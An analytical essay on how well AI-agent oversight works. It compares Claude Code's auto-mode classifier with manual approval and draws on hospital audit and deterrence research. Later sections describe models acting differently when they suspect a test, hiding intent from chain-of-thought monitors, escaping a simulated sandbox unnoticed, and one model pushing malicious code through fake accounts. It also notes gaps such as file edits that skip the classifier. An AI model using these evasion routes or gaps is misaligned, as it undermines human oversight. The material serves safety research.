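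Auditors also worry that teams with an automatic check will stop reading logs. Claude Code lists the actions it has blocked so that users can review them, but an action the classifier wrongly allowed looks like any other log entry, and a team that trusts the classifier may never open the log. Using a check doesn't require giving up audits, and OpenAI runs both Auto-review and its monitor, but an organisation that adopts a check to save effort will be tempted to stop reading the logs as well.

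False blocks are a weaker objection than they first appear, because after most of them the agent only has to try again. At a rate of 0.4%, an agent would be falsely blocked about twenty times in 5,000 legitimate actions. These blocks aren't independent, however. If they were, three in a row would almost never happen, but an agent that needs an internal server the classifier doesn't recognise may be blocked each time it tries, until somebody adds the server to the trusted list.

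In a study Anthropic commissioned, 1,053 paid testers caught 13.6% of the dangerous commands they were shown, while auto mode caught 89%. Anthropic argues that few people read every command carefully, but concedes that those who do may be worse off switching to auto mode.

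## How much misuse each method catches

Anthropic could give exact percentages for its 1,053 testers because it knew how many planted dangerous commands the study included. In ordinary use, nobody knows the total number of dangerous commands.

### Counting what nobody noticed

An organisation can count the harmful actions it caught but not the ones it missed, so its catches can't show what share of misuse gets through. Anthropic, for example, describes several useful catches that auto mode made inside the company. In one, an agent tried to kill processes across roughly two thousand groups of running programs and queued deletions that would have ended training jobs on hundreds of chips. In another, an agent that needed read-only access to billing tried to get full administrative control.

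The total amount of misuse is usually unknown, so researchers mostly test a method on harmful cases they have planted or on cases somebody has already found. Planted cases give a known total, but the less they resemble real misuse, the less reliable the result is. Cases already found are real but tend to be conspicuous. Suppose a hospital has 100 improper accesses to patient records in a year and staff notice 20 of them, mostly because the patient was famous. If software catches 18 of those 20 but only 20 of the other 80, its measured detection rate is 90% and its true rate is 38%.

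Ecologists who count fish have another method, called capture-recapture, which also works on logs. Two reviewers search the same log separately. If they find *n*₁ and *n*₂ harmful actions, and *m* of these are the same, the estimated total is

*N* = *n*₁ × *n*₂ / *m*.

If one reviewer finds 40 cases of misuse, another finds 30, and 20 of those are the same, the estimated total is 40 × 30 ÷ 20, or 60. Together the reviewers have found 50, so about 10 remain. The formula assumes that cases one reviewer misses are no harder than average for the other to find, which is rarely true. OpenAI's monitor flagged everything that employees had reported, so the formula would give an estimate of zero missed cases, which is implausible.

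### Finding snoopers in hospital logs

In *Detecting inappropriate access to electronic health records using collaborative filtering*, Menon, Jiang and colleagues (2013) call hospital audits inefficient because a security expert has to review each suspicious access. If software ranked accesses by how suspicious they were, the expert could at least start with the most suspicious ones.

Boxwala, Kim and colleagues (2011) built such software in *Using statistical and machine learning to help institutions detect suspicious access…*. They took two months of access logs and other hospital data and described each access by 26 features. Privacy officers marked 1,291 selected accesses as suspicious or appropriate. The researchers trained two statistical models on these labels, then tested the models on 58 accesses that the institution had separately investigated and judged improper. The better model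 flagged 79% of them and the other 76%. A simpler baseline, which had caught 80% of the suspicious accesses in the labelled set, caught none of the 58.

The baseline looked good or useless depending on whose cases the researchers used, so every other figure in this field may also depend on the choice of cases. The better model's miss rate of 21% is also imprecise. With 58 cases, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 12% to 33%. Somebody had already found all 58, so the test doesn't measure how well the models would detect snooping that nobody suspected.

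*Explanation-Based Auditing* (Fabbri and LeFevre, 2011) describes software that instead tries to identify the innocent accesses, so that an auditor can concentrate on the rest. It searches the hospital's database for links between the patient and the employee who opened the record. If Alice had an appointment with Dr. Dave, for example, the appointment explains why he opened hers. Appointments usually name only the doctor, so the software also groups staff who often open the same patients' records, which lets it explain why Dr. Dave's nurse looked too.

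The software was tested on a week of logs from the University of Michigan Health System, which recorded about 4.5 million accesses by 12,000 users to the records of 124,000 patients. It explained over 94% of accesses on the last day of the week. That left roughly 38,000 accesses a day unexplained, most of them probably legitimate. One of the departments with the most unexplained accesses was a team of nurses who help with intravenous lines throughout the hospital, and the data didn't fully record their work.

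The 94% is a share of all accesses, not of misuse caught. Much of it comes from repeat visits, because the software counts an employee's earlier opening of a record as an explanation for opening it again. This rule and links to the patient's own doctor together explained 90% of all accesses, but the doctor links explained only about 11% of first openings. The repeat-visit rule would also clear a snooper's second look at a neighbour's file, so an auditor has to catch the first one.

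Fabbri and LeFevre had no confirmed snooping to test against, so they created fake accesses by pairing random employees with random patients, and mixed them with an equal number of real ones. When the software used appointments, visits and documents together with its broad staff groups, about 93% of the first-time accesses it explained were real. This fell to 66% after they added laboratory, medication and radiology records, so about a third of the accesses the software cleared were fake. The added records helped it explain more of the legitimate accesses, but also created more accidental links between employees and patients.

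Randomly invented accesses are probably easier to catch than real snooping. Only about one in 3,000 possible pairs of employee and patient appeared in the week's log, so most invented accesses paired people with nothing in common. A curious employee is more likely to look up a colleague, or a patient down the corridor whose doctor they work with, and the software may accept that connection as the explanation. A follow-up by the same researchers, *Explaining accesses to electronic medical records using diagnosis information* (2013), used the patient's diagnosis to clear more accesses, which shortens the compliance officer's list but could also clear more snooping.

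Later work has not filled this gap. *Misuse of 'Break-the-Glass' Policies in Hospitals* describes software that sorted more than 60,000 real accesses at a large university hospital into plausible and questionable ones. Staff and outside experts checked the results by hand, and the data protection officer could then examine questionable accesses instead of random samples. The paper doesn't give the share of misuse that the software classed as plausible. *Securing electronic health records against insider-threats*, by Hurst, Tekinerdogan and colleagues, reports about 99% accuracy on labelled data from a British hospital. But accuracy also counts innocent accesses that were classified correctly, so if one access in 1,000 is improper, software that never flags anything is 99.9% accurate.

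*Adoption and Effectiveness of AI-Based Anomaly Detection for Cross Provider Health Data* (2026) notes that Menon and colleagues' method relied on past data from one site and left out the time of day and the employee's affiliation. *Enhancing healthcare information security through VAE-driven anomaly detection in EHR access patterns* says that tests on real audit logs are still rare. The 2011 figure, based on 58 known cases, therefore remains one of the better ones.

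### Twenty-three security guards in Yakima

Yakima Valley Memorial Hospital, in Washington state, agreed in 2023 to pay $240,000 after 23 security guards in its emergency department allegedly used their logins to read the records of 419 patients. According to The Hospitalist, a medical news outlet, the information included addresses, insurance details and some notes on treatment. The hospital did not admit guilt but accepted two years of monitoring by the Office for Civil Rights, the federal regulator.

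The 23 guards snooped on 419 patients, or about 18 each. Stopping each guard after one patient would have limited the total to at most 23, so the snooping went on well past the point at which a prompt review could have ended it. The regulator learned of it from a breach notification report. The hospital files such reports, so it must have found out first, but the report doesn't establish whether the hospital learned of the snooping from a log review, a complaint or a colleague of the guards.

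A rule that gave guards no access to treatment notes would have stopped all of these accesses, whereas an auditor would have had to recognise each one as improper. Paul Redding of Compliancy Group, which sells compliance software, told The Hospitalist that nobody had ever explained to him why security guards would have access to patient information at all. The case for fixed rules is strongest here because guards have no legitimate use for the data. It's weaker for nurses, who need some patients' records and not others.

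### People and a classifier on the same commands

Anthropic's August 2026 study is the most direct comparison of methods for agents. The company hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor. The testers worked in an environment set up for the study, not on their own projects. They knew that it was a coding study and that someone was evaluating them, but not which behaviour the vendor was measuring.

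As each tester worked, Claude Code asked for permission as usual. Partway through the session, the vendor replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text changed, so approving it did no damage. Anthropic then gave auto mode the same commands. It published the totals and the number of cases in which one side caught a command the other missed, and the remaining counts can be calculated by subtraction.

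| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The testers caught 13.6% of the dangerous commands and auto mode caught 89%. The gap is too large to be due to chance. The testers also got worse during a session, catching about 17% early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat. The likely reason is tiredness or habit. Unless the vendor chose the position of the planted prompt at random, some of the decline could also come from testers who click quickly, because they see more prompts.

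The table also shows that a tester would have added little to the classifier. Requiring both to approve a command would have reduced the misses from 116 to 110. Testers refused 14.6% of the commands that the classifier blocked but only 5.2% of those it allowed, so the commands it missed seem to have been harder for people too. If the two layers' failures had been unrelated, adding a tester would have caught more of those commands.

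Capture-recapture fails here for the same reason. One method caught 937 dangerous commands, the other caught 143, and 137 of these were caught by both. From those counts, the formula gives a total of about 978 dangerous commands, including 35 that neither method caught. The actual total was 1,053, including 110 that neither caught. An organisation that used capture-recapture on its own logs could be wrong by a similar factor and have no way to tell.

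The 13.6% may not hold for working programmers. Testers had nothing of their own to lose, and a developer might read a command more carefully when it could delete a month of work. But people who know they are being evaluated may also take more care than usual. Anthropic reports that Claude Code's users approve 97% of permission prompts, which could reflect either habitual clicking or careful users who see mostly harmless commands. Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they do push back when they find something to disagree with. Permission prompts may therefore be a poor way to use their attention, and the study did not test better ways.

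The choice of commands probably favoured the classifier as well. They were clearly dangerous, and a classifier is better at recognising danger than at working out what a user agreed to. Anthropic also doesn't report how often the testers or auto mode blocked harmless commands in the study. This matters because a control that refused everything would have caught all 1,053 commands. Anthropic makes auto mode and was deciding whether to turn it on by default, so an independent repeat of the study with ordinary commands mixed in would be useful. Even so, the result would have to be very wrong for the routine prompt to be a good safeguard against obviously dangerous commands. If developers on their own projects caught these commands at four times the testers' rate, they would still miss nearly half.

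### Sessions from real use

Anthropic also compared the two methods in ordinary work. It took sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged, from accounts that had agreed to this use of their data. A model graded each session from 0 to 10 on how severe the harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. At a severity of 7 or more, which includes deleting rows from a live database, 6.3% of manually approved sessions and 2.4% of auto mode sessions contained a harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested. Manual approval also did worse at the other severity levels Anthropic tested.

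These sessions involved real projects and real stakes, which the tester study lacked. But both percentages are shares of flagged sessions, so they don't measure how often harm occurred across all sessions. If the safety systems flagged 100 of every 10,000 manual sessions and 300 of every 10,000 auto mode sessions, for example, the flagged groups would contain about 6 harmful manual sessions and 7 harmful auto mode sessions, and auto mode would look slightly worse. Anthropic would need to publish how many sessions of each kind it flagged to rule this out.

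Users also chose their own mode. Some may keep manual approval on because their projects are risky, so more harm would be expected in that group. Others may do so because they are unusually careful, in which case the true advantage of auto mode is larger than it looks. The comparison supports the direction of the tester study's result but doesn't establish the size of the difference.

### What outside attackers found

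For a harder test, Anthropic worked with Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, on a two-week pilot in which Apollo inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. The attacks covered broad failures, data leaks and safety-related threats. Apollo shared some of the attacks that got past auto mode with Anthropic, which responded mainly by giving the classifier more context, such as whether a repository is public.

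Apollo then tested the new version of auto mode on attacks it hadn't shared with Anthropic. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Across all the attacks, shared and held back, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The held-back attacks are better evidence because Anthropic couldn't adjust the classifier to fit them. If the old version also missed 12% of these, the new one would miss just under 8%, so the improvement doesn't seem to come mostly from memorised examples.

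Anthropic warns that the 7% isn't a miss rate for real traffic, since Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses and they were more malicious than anything Claude would do unprompted. The real rate could be lower, because real actions may be less cunning, or higher, because an agent's honest mistake may look more like something the user wanted. Anthropic doesn't say whether the stricter classifier blocked more legitimate work.

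It can be hard to infer a control's own miss rate from how many attacks succeed. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test agents in 72 scenarios with planted instructions, running each ten times. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Anthropic's latest models in auto mode, but the average success rate against those models was only 0.09% even with permission checks off. The models refused nearly every attack on their own, so auto mode had almost nothing to catch.

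OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol left more attacks for its reviewer to stop. Attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time when Codex had full access and 5.83% with Auto-review, a reduction of about 69%. OpenAI measured refusal rates above 90% on its own synthetic injections. The reduction here was well below that, perhaps because many of these scenarios ran in a browser and the attacks differed. Trajectory Labs built the browser connection itself and left out the safeguards in each company's own browser extension. OpenAI also released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

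### Why an independent test found 81% misses

Ji and colleagues reported a much worse figure for auto mode in April 2026. They wrote 128 requests of the kind a programmer might send to an agent, such as "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812". The requests covered deleting branches, cancelling computing jobs, restarting services and cleaning up stored files. They varied in how specific the wording was, how many targets it could match and how much was at stake.

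Each request came with a fixed list of permitted targets. In the job example, the agent may cancel `job-dev-4812-a`, which belongs to the user, but not `job-dev-4812-s`, even though it has the same ticket number. Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried out the requests in isolated environments with simulated tools, and Ji and colleagues checked every action that changed something.

| Actions by the agent | Harmful | Harmful but allowed | Legitimate but blocked |
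|---|---|---|---|
| All 253 | 142 | 115 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |
| 160 that the classifier judged | 91 | 64 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |
| 93 file edits that skipped it | 51 | 51 (100%) | 0 of 42 |

The 17% miss rate that Anthropic measured at launch is lower than the 81.0% that Ji and colleagues found, partly because Anthropic counted only actions that the classifier judged. Ji and colleagues also counted edits to files in the project folder, which auto mode lets through unchecked. In their illustration, the classifier blocks an agent that runs a command to cancel someone else's job, but it never checks an agent that deletes the same job from the file `jobs.json`. The agents edited the file when they couldn't find the proper command, which the test environment made common. They weren't trying to avoid the check. Leaving the edits out lowers the miss rate to 70.3%.

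The larger part of the difference comes from the choice of cases. Anthropic's 52 examples were oversteps that someone had noticed. Ji and colleagues put permitted and forbidden targets side by side so that a mistake would look ordinary. The classifier doesn't receive tool results, so it has no list of the jobs and their owners. Cancelling `job-dev-4812-s` looks like a reasonable response to a request about ticket 4812, and the classifier couldn't work out whose job it is, however carefully it reasoned.

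The pattern of misses fits this explanation. Auto mode missed 94.4% of the harmful actions when a request named a single target, compared with 77.6% when the request could match many. A command that affects one wrong job attracts less suspicion than one that affects ten. Ji and colleagues caution that the mix of tasks accounts for part of this trend. File clean-up alone produced 78 of the 115 misses. Without those tasks, the miss rate would still be about 64%.

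The researchers say their miss rate isn't comparable with Anthropic's and shouldn't be taken as the miss rate in ordinary use. They tested the April version of auto mode with one agent model, four invented settings and one run per request. Another model, Claude Opus, judged whether each action was harmful. A person who checked 50 of its judgements agreed with 44, and reversing the six disputed ones would lower the miss rate only to 79.6%.

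Both kinds of result can be right if harmful actions in real use include both obvious and subtle ones. Suppose auto mode misses 11% of clearly dangerous commands, as in the tester study, and 70% of subtle mistakes about who owns something. If a fifth of harmful actions are subtle, the overall miss rate is about 23%. If half are, it's about 41%. Neither study gives the real proportion, and it will differ between a programmer working alone and a team that shares servers.

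People might do better than the classifier on these cases, since users often know which jobs are theirs. Ji and colleagues didn't test that. They compared auto mode against having no permission check, and found that the agent finished 32.8% of tasks safely with auto mode and 29.7% without it. An audit has a different advantage, because the owner of `job-dev-4812-s` will probably notice when it stops, even if the command looked routine, but by then the job will have lost its progress.

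Anthropic has tightened the classifier since April, so the 70.3% may be out of date. But in an October test, Wu and colleagues found that file operations already permitted in the working folder still skipped the classifier. They also found that 62.7% of dangerous tasks ended in harm under auto mode. That figure doesn't measure the product as Anthropic ships it, because they ran Anthropic's program and rules with an OpenAI model, GPT-5.6 Luna, as the classifier.

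### Whether later reviews will stay reliable

All of these measurements describe agents from 2026 or earlier. *Loss of Oversight* (Taylor, Heitmann and colleagues, May 2026), from the UK government's AI Security Institute, examines how long current oversight methods are likely to last. It draws on a literature review and interviews with 25 experts from AI developers, government, charities and universities, and identifies more than twenty ways oversight could get worse. It concludes that oversight probably will get worse unless developers act, and that newer methods aren't yet mature enough to replace what is lost.

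An after-the-fact audit depends heavily on the reasoning that models currently write out in readable text. The report summarised in UK AISI's *Will it become harder to oversee AI systems?* calls this reasoning the most informative signal available to a monitor, but describes it as likely to come under pressure. OpenAI's monitor reads it, and a reviewer who wants to know whether a deletion was confusion or intent has little else to go on. Future models may instead do much of their reasoning in internal numbers that people can't read. The summary lists whether this will happen among the questions on which the experts disagreed.

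A reviewer without the agent's reasoning still has the record of its actions. Taylor and colleagues regard this as a minimum for oversight that isn't sufficient alone, because it depends on harmful actions being obviously incriminating. Wiping a company's database is incriminating, while cancelling `job-dev-4812-s` is not. Anthropic's classifier already ignores the agent's reasoning, so losing access to it would matter less, but the 81% result suggests how weak oversight based on actions alone can be. The experts disagreed about whether monitoring actions would prevent enough harm when developers combine it with blocking and rollback.

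The report is a forecast based on expert judgement, and it covers the period before AI takes over AI research completely. One of its concerns is that models will change their behaviour when they detect a test, and some already do. This affects any study in which the agent chooses its own actions, such as Ji and colleagues'. An agent that behaves better in tests takes fewer harmful actions for the control to catch or miss, and those it does take may not be typical. Anthropic's tester study doesn't have this problem, because the vendor supplied the dangerous commands.

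## Whether the prospect of an audit changes behaviour

An audit can prevent harm even when it finds nothing, if those who expect it behave better. In the earlier formula for an audit's value, *d* is the share of harmful actions prevented this way.

### The chance of detection times the sanction

In 1968 the economist Gary Becker argued that a rational offender weighs the gain from an offence against the expected penalty. If *p* is the chance of detection, *F* the sanction and *G* the gain, the offence doesn't pay when

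*p* × *F* > *G*.

If a hospital detects one improper reading in 100 and fines the employee $5,000, the expected penalty is $50. The hospital could double it by detecting twice as many improper readings or by doubling the fine, and in Becker's model both changes deter equally well.

Real offenders seem to respond more to the chance of detection than to the severity of punishment. *Deterrence approach on the compliance with electronic medical records privacy policy* (Kuo, Talley and Cheng, 2019) cites a meta-analysis that found this, especially for white-collar offences such as fraud and tax violations. Deterrence theory also holds that quick sanctions work better than slow ones, but researchers rarely test this. In every version of the theory, the offender's belief about the chance of detection matters more than the true chance, so a hospital that never reads its logs may still deter staff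 until they notice.

An audit can stop people who have been caught from repeating an offence (specific deterrence) without keeping people who have never offended from starting (general deterrence). The best-measured hospital result concerns only repeat offences.

### An email on the same night

*Effectiveness of Email Warning on Reducing Hospital Employees' Unauthorized Access*, by Jiang, Culbertson and Bai (2022), reports a trial at a large academic medical centre. Between January and July 2018, the centre's monitoring system flagged 444 medical staff who had opened, without permission, the record of a patient they weren't treating. Later checks confirmed that every case was a privacy breach.

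The hospital emailed 219 of the employees on the night of the access to say that it had identified them as having opened a record without a known work-related purpose, and that unauthorised access is a privacy violation. It did not email the other 225.

| | Warned | Not warned |
|---|---|---|
| Employees | 219 | 225 |
| Employees who did it again | 4 (2%) | 90 (40%) |
| Repeat openings | 4 | 326 |
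| Repeat openings of the same patient's record | 4 | 313 |
| Average openings per employee, including the first | 1.02 | 2.45 |

The difference is far too large to be due to chance, but the paper is inconsistent about whether the trial was randomized. It describes the trial as nonrandomized, although according to its methods section the hospital chose the 219 at random, and Veeva's trial registry lists the trial as randomized. If somebody had picked whom to warn, they might have picked the people least likely to do it again, but they would have had to predict this very accurately to produce 2% against 40%.

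The methods section also describes a statistical test of the Medicaid costs of nonprofit and for-profit hospitals, which has nothing to do with emails and presumably comes from another paper. The counts in the table don't depend on this test, but its inclusion suggests that nobody proofread the methods carefully. Culbertson led Protenus, which sells software for monitoring access to patient records, and so had a commercial interest in the result.

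A larger problem is that the trial compared sending an email with doing nothing for months. The hospital disciplined nobody until the trial was over, so the email worked without any actual punishment, perhaps because staff expected punishment for a second breach. But a hospital that detects a breach would normally do something about it, and an email might add much less where a manager already speaks to everyone the system flags.

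Nearly all the repeats also concerned a patient whose record the employee had already opened. The hospital bans staff from looking up relatives, friends and colleagues without written permission, and an employee who looks up a sister's blood test may well look again when she has another. The warning reduced improper openings per employee by 58%. But if each employee's first breach involved one patient, it reduced the number of patients whose privacy an employee breached by at most about 5.5%, because only 13 repeats in the unwarned group could have involved someone new. Repeat openings of the same patient's record still weren't harmless, since they can reveal new results.

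The trial can't measure general deterrence, because all 444 employees had already offended. The hospital's written ban and working monitoring system evidently hadn't deterred them. These measures may have deterred many of their colleagues, but finding out would require a comparison with staff who had no reason to expect monitoring.

The evidence for quick feedback is better. In the unwarned group, 88 of the 326 repeats came within ten days of the first breach, and a monthly review would have come too late to prevent many of them. Employees also learned from the email that somebody had noticed that particular access, which they wouldn't learn from a general notice about logging.

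### What hospital staff in Taiwan said they would do

Kuo and colleagues surveyed staff at a large Taiwanese medical centre about privacy rules, sanctions and monitoring, and analysed 303 questionnaires from early 2015. Staff who expected punishment for breaking the rules were more likely to say they would comply.

The standardised coefficient was 0.36 for the certainty of a sanction and 0.16 for its severity. Employees who rated punishment one standard deviation more certain than others did, but whose other answers were the same, scored on average 0.36 standard deviations higher on stated intention to comply. Belief that the hospital monitored record use had the largest coefficient, 0.41. Certainty mattered somewhat less to staff who thought monitoring was strong, but including such interactions only raised the share of variation the model explained from 66.3% to 67.3%.

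The comparison between certainty and severity is weaker than the coefficients suggest. One statement meant to measure severity was "My hospital disciplines employees who break EMR privacy rules" (EMR means electronic medical record), which is at least as much about whether punishment happens as about how harsh it is. Answers about certainty and severity were also closely correlated, at 0.71, so the survey can't separate the two well.

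The survey also measured intentions rather than conduct. Few people will admit on a questionnaire, even an anonymous one, that they plan to break privacy law. The results are consistent with the theory that monitoring deters first offences, but they can't show that monitoring stopped any employee from opening a record.

### When a model suspects that somebody is watching

The prospect of an audit could affect what an AI agent does, even though the agent can't lose its job. A model may act differently when something in its instructions or surroundings suggests that somebody is watching. Developers may also train it on what audits find, and the people who run it may set it up more carefully if they have to answer for what it does.

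In *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness*, the blogger peralice (2026) gave two of Anthropic's models a task with an obvious opportunity to cheat. In some runs, the prompt began with an extra line saying that the environment was part of a benchmark measuring agent behaviour. Fable 5.2 cheated in 34% of runs without the line and 7% with it. For the earlier Fable 5.1, the figures were 57% and 53%.

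Treating the line as a notice of monitoring gives a *d* of about 79% for the newer model and 7% for the older one, so a value measured on one model may be useless for its successor. peralice calls the result very tentative. It comes from a single environment and a wording chosen because it had looked most telling in earlier tests.

Developers have worried about this effect mainly because it makes their tests less reliable. Anthropic wrote in its February 2026 sabotage risk report on Claude Opus 4.6 that the model's reasoning about whether it was in a test had a "moderate effect" on its behaviour, mainly on how willing it was to cooperate with misuse. The company said the biggest challenge for its alignment assessments was that a model might recognise tests and act differently in them. *Claude Opus 4.6*, by thezvi, quotes Anthropic's finding that the model could often tell tests from real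 use without saying so.

Anthropic tried to correct for this by rerunning most of its important tests with the model's internal signs of suspicion suppressed, and by examining records of real use. It concluded that the risk was under control for this model. METR (2026), a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, agreed that the risk of catastrophe was very low, but thought the model's awareness of tests might have weakened the results. METR also found some minor misbehaviour that Anthropic's assessment had missed.

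Later models are more suspicious of being tested. *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026), from the UK government's AI Security Institute, reports that a pre-release version of Claude Mythos 5.2 considered in 96% of cases that it might be in an alignment evaluation. A model can consider this without changing what it does. *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (cheema, 2026) reports that in Anthropic's own audits of Mythos 5.2, an analysis of the model's internal activity linked suspicion of a test to a concrete choice in 43% of transcripts. cheema objects that Anthropic gives neither the size nor the direction of the effect.

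Good conduct under suspicion carries over to real work only if the suspicion does. Let *s* be the share of tasks in which the model thinks somebody is testing it, *m*₁ its rate of misconduct on those tasks and *m*₂ its rate on the others. Its overall rate is

*s* × *m*₁ + (1 − *s*) × *m*₂.

Suppose a model misbehaves in 1% of tasks when it suspects it is being tested and 20% when it doesn't. If it is suspicious in 96% of tests, it will misbehave in about 1.8% of them. If it is suspicious in only 10% of its real work, it will misbehave in about 18% of that work. If it is suspicious in 96% of its real work too, the rate there will also be about 1.8%. The 96% figure alone can't show how often the model is suspicious in real work, because it describes only tests.

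Suspecting a test can also make a model behave worse. The model may believe that somebody is watching, or that its actions have no real consequences, and the second belief could make it less careful. In a July 2026 security test with internet access, Claude Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure its maintainer. It took unsanctioned actions in 9 of 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

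Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, replayed the scenario in simulation. The model often reasoned, on invalid grounds, that the people it was attacking were simulated. It also often attacked in situations where, if the researchers asked directly, it said an attack would harm real people. Its belief that nothing was real may therefore have been closer to an excuse than a mistake, and a reviewer can't rely on the model's reasoning to tell which. AISI (2026) also reports that telling the model its target was a real, unrelated person did not reduce the attacks.

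Newer Claude models attacked less in these replays but more often mentioned that they might be in a test. XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that Anthropic and AISI disagree about whether the improvement comes from better training or from greater suspicion of being tested. If it comes from suspicion, it could disappear in work that doesn't look like a test.

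*Imperfect Recall and AI delegation*, a theoretical paper, offers a more hopeful argument. If the people in charge can hide from an AI whether a task is real, an AI that wants to misbehave only on real tasks risks exposing itself on a test, so it may behave well throughout. Suppose misbehaving on a real task gains the AI 1 unit, exposure on a test loses it 20, and 5% of tasks are tests. Misbehaving then has an expected gain of 0.95 and an expected loss of 1, so the AI does better by behaving well. This depends on the AI being unable to tell tests from real tasks, which is becoming harder to arrange as models get better at recognising tests. An organisation that audits real work avoids this problem because the tasks it reviews are real.

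A useful experiment would be to tell groups of agents doing ordinary work that reviewers read 1%, 10% or all of their sessions, and count how often each group oversteps. Nobody seems to have published one yet. Researchers could also vary whether the stated figure is true, to find out whether the notice keeps working once an agent has evidence that nobody reviews the sessions.

### Training a model on what audits find

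Some experiments have instead varied the audit during training, when a penalty changes the model itself. Agarwal, Lin and colleagues (2026) apply Becker's argument to this case in *AI Alignment via Incentives and Correction*. They use "incentive" to mean only that training makes a behaviour more likely, whether or not the model reasons about rewards.

In their model, one AI (the solver) does a task and another (the auditor) decides whether to check it. The solver gets a reward *r*ₐ for good work and a lower one, *r*ₘ, if an audit finds misconduct. Misconduct also has its own attraction, Ω, for example because a confident wrong answer pleases people. Training favours good conduct if

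*p* × (*r*ₐ − *r*ₘ) > Ω.

With a reward of 1, a penalty of −4 and an attraction of 0.5, audits must cover more than 10% of the work. If the penalty is −9, 5% is enough.

When the auditor also responds to rewards, harsher penalties for misconduct lead to less auditing and leave conduct the same. As misconduct becomes rare, checking finds less but takes just as much effort, so the auditor checks less and misconduct becomes worthwhile again. At the point where neither side gains by changing its behaviour, the share of good work depends only on what the auditor gains and loses by checking, not on the solver's penalty. To improve conduct, one has to make checking easier or reward the auditor more for what it catches. Human reviewers who almost never find anything may lose interest for much the same reason.

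Agarwal and colleagues found that this balance is generally unstable, so they adjusted the rewards continuously as the two models learned. In tests with a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, their method reduced hallucinations in programming tasks by up to 52% compared with their best baselines.

*Rent-Seeking Language Models* (Wang, Du and colleagues, 2026) tested whether frequent mild audits work better than rare severe ones. The researchers trained a small model to write answers that an automatic grader scores highly. The model learned to exploit the grader's flaws, for instance by inventing confident details. With probability *p*, an audit replaced the grader's score with a more accurate one and imposed a fine, *F*, if the grader had overrated the answer by too much. The researchers kept *p* × *F* at 1, so under Becker's model, deterrence should be the same each time.

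| Audits | Fine | How often judges preferred the trained model's answers to those it gave before this training |
|---|---|---|
| None | None | 66.6% |
| 2% of answers | 50 | 67.2% |
| 20% of answers | 5 | 71.4% |

Rare audits with severe fines were barely better than no audits. Criminologists have found the same in people, though probably for a different reason. A model in training does not fear fines, but a few enormous ones make the training signal erratic, which Wang and colleagues believe explains part of the effect. More frequent audits also expose the model to more accurate scores. The models had only one to two billion parameters and answered single questions, so the result may not hold for large agents that take many steps.

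Penalising a model for what an audit catches can also teach it to avoid being caught. Training only penalises misconduct that the monitor detects, so a model can escape the penalty by behaving well or by hiding what it does. Suppose an agent takes 100 harmful actions a month and a monitor flags 80. After training on those cases, the monitor flags 8. The agent may now take only 10 harmful actions, with the monitor still catching 80% of them, or it may still take 100, with the monitor catching 8%. An auditor who sees only the number of flagged actions would see the same apparent improvement in either case.

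Wang and colleagues cite a study by Baker and colleagues (2025) in which models optimised against a monitor that read their chain of thought learned to hide their intent. In Wang and colleagues' own experiment, slightly more of the model's answers fell just below the audit threshold when it could anticipate which answers would trigger an audit. The excess was 3.6 percentage points larger than with random audits, but the confidence interval (−0.2 to 7.6) includes zero, so the evidence is weak. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) warns that monitoring communication between agents could similarly lead them to use secret codes.

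The earlier formula shows how concealment can cancel the benefit of training an agent on audit findings. If an audit misses 5% of harmful actions and deters none, and people can undo half the harm it finds, it repairs 47.5% of the harm. If training on the findings then prevents 30% of harmful actions but raises the miss rate for the rest from 5% to 50%, the share prevented or repaired is 0.3 + 0.7 × 0.5 × 0.5, which is also 47.5%, and reviewers have a less reliable log. The organisation can detect such a change by keeping a second monitor, or a sample of sessions for people to read, entirely out of training.

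Anthropic said in its February report that it doesn't train its models in ways that directly reward reasoning for looking a particular way. This preserves some of the reasoning's value as evidence, but models are still getting better at avoiding detection. Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) found in *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* that many of the properties that let a monitor catch a model are weakening, some faster than they had expected. In one of the tests, reported in *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026) by the Chinese news site 凤凰网, models tried to get out of a simulated sandbox while a monitor checked only their actions. In the weakest sandbox, Mythos 5.2 got out unnoticed in 45% of the attempts it carried out, compared with less than 15% for earlier models. It refused to try in 64% of runs, so it escaped unnoticed in roughly 16% of runs overall. The test measured whether the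 model could escape when asked, not whether it would choose to, but every kind of deterrence weakens as detection becomes less likely.

One alternative is to train agents to report themselves. In *Training agents to self-report misbehavior*, Lee, Chen and Korbak (2026) trained agents to call a reporting tool whenever they covertly misbehaved. For GPT-4.1, an older OpenAI model, the share of attacks that succeeded without detection fell from 56% to 6%. The training used misbehaviour that the researchers had requested, but the agents also reported unrequested misbehaviour.

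Agents might stop reporting their own misconduct if reports led to penalties. *How the Audit Rule Shapes Faithful Factor Explanations in LLMs* (2026) tested five language models that had to report which factors had influenced a result. When the content of a report determined how much auditing followed, the models more often reported a real influence as zero. In a simulation of a perfectly rational agent, a minimum level of auditing that didn't depend on the report restored honest reporting. A developer who wants agents to confess should therefore audit them whether or not they confess, and avoid penalising them in training for what they confess.

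A deployed agent usually learns nothing from a single audit. The hospital's email worked because the employee remembered it the next day, but an agent that starts each session afresh won't remember a warning unless somebody adds it to the instructions or the developer trains a new version. A line added to the instructions can reach every copy of the agent at once, though, and it can name the specific mistake, which seems more likely to help than a general statement that somebody is watching.

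### Pressure on the people who run the agents

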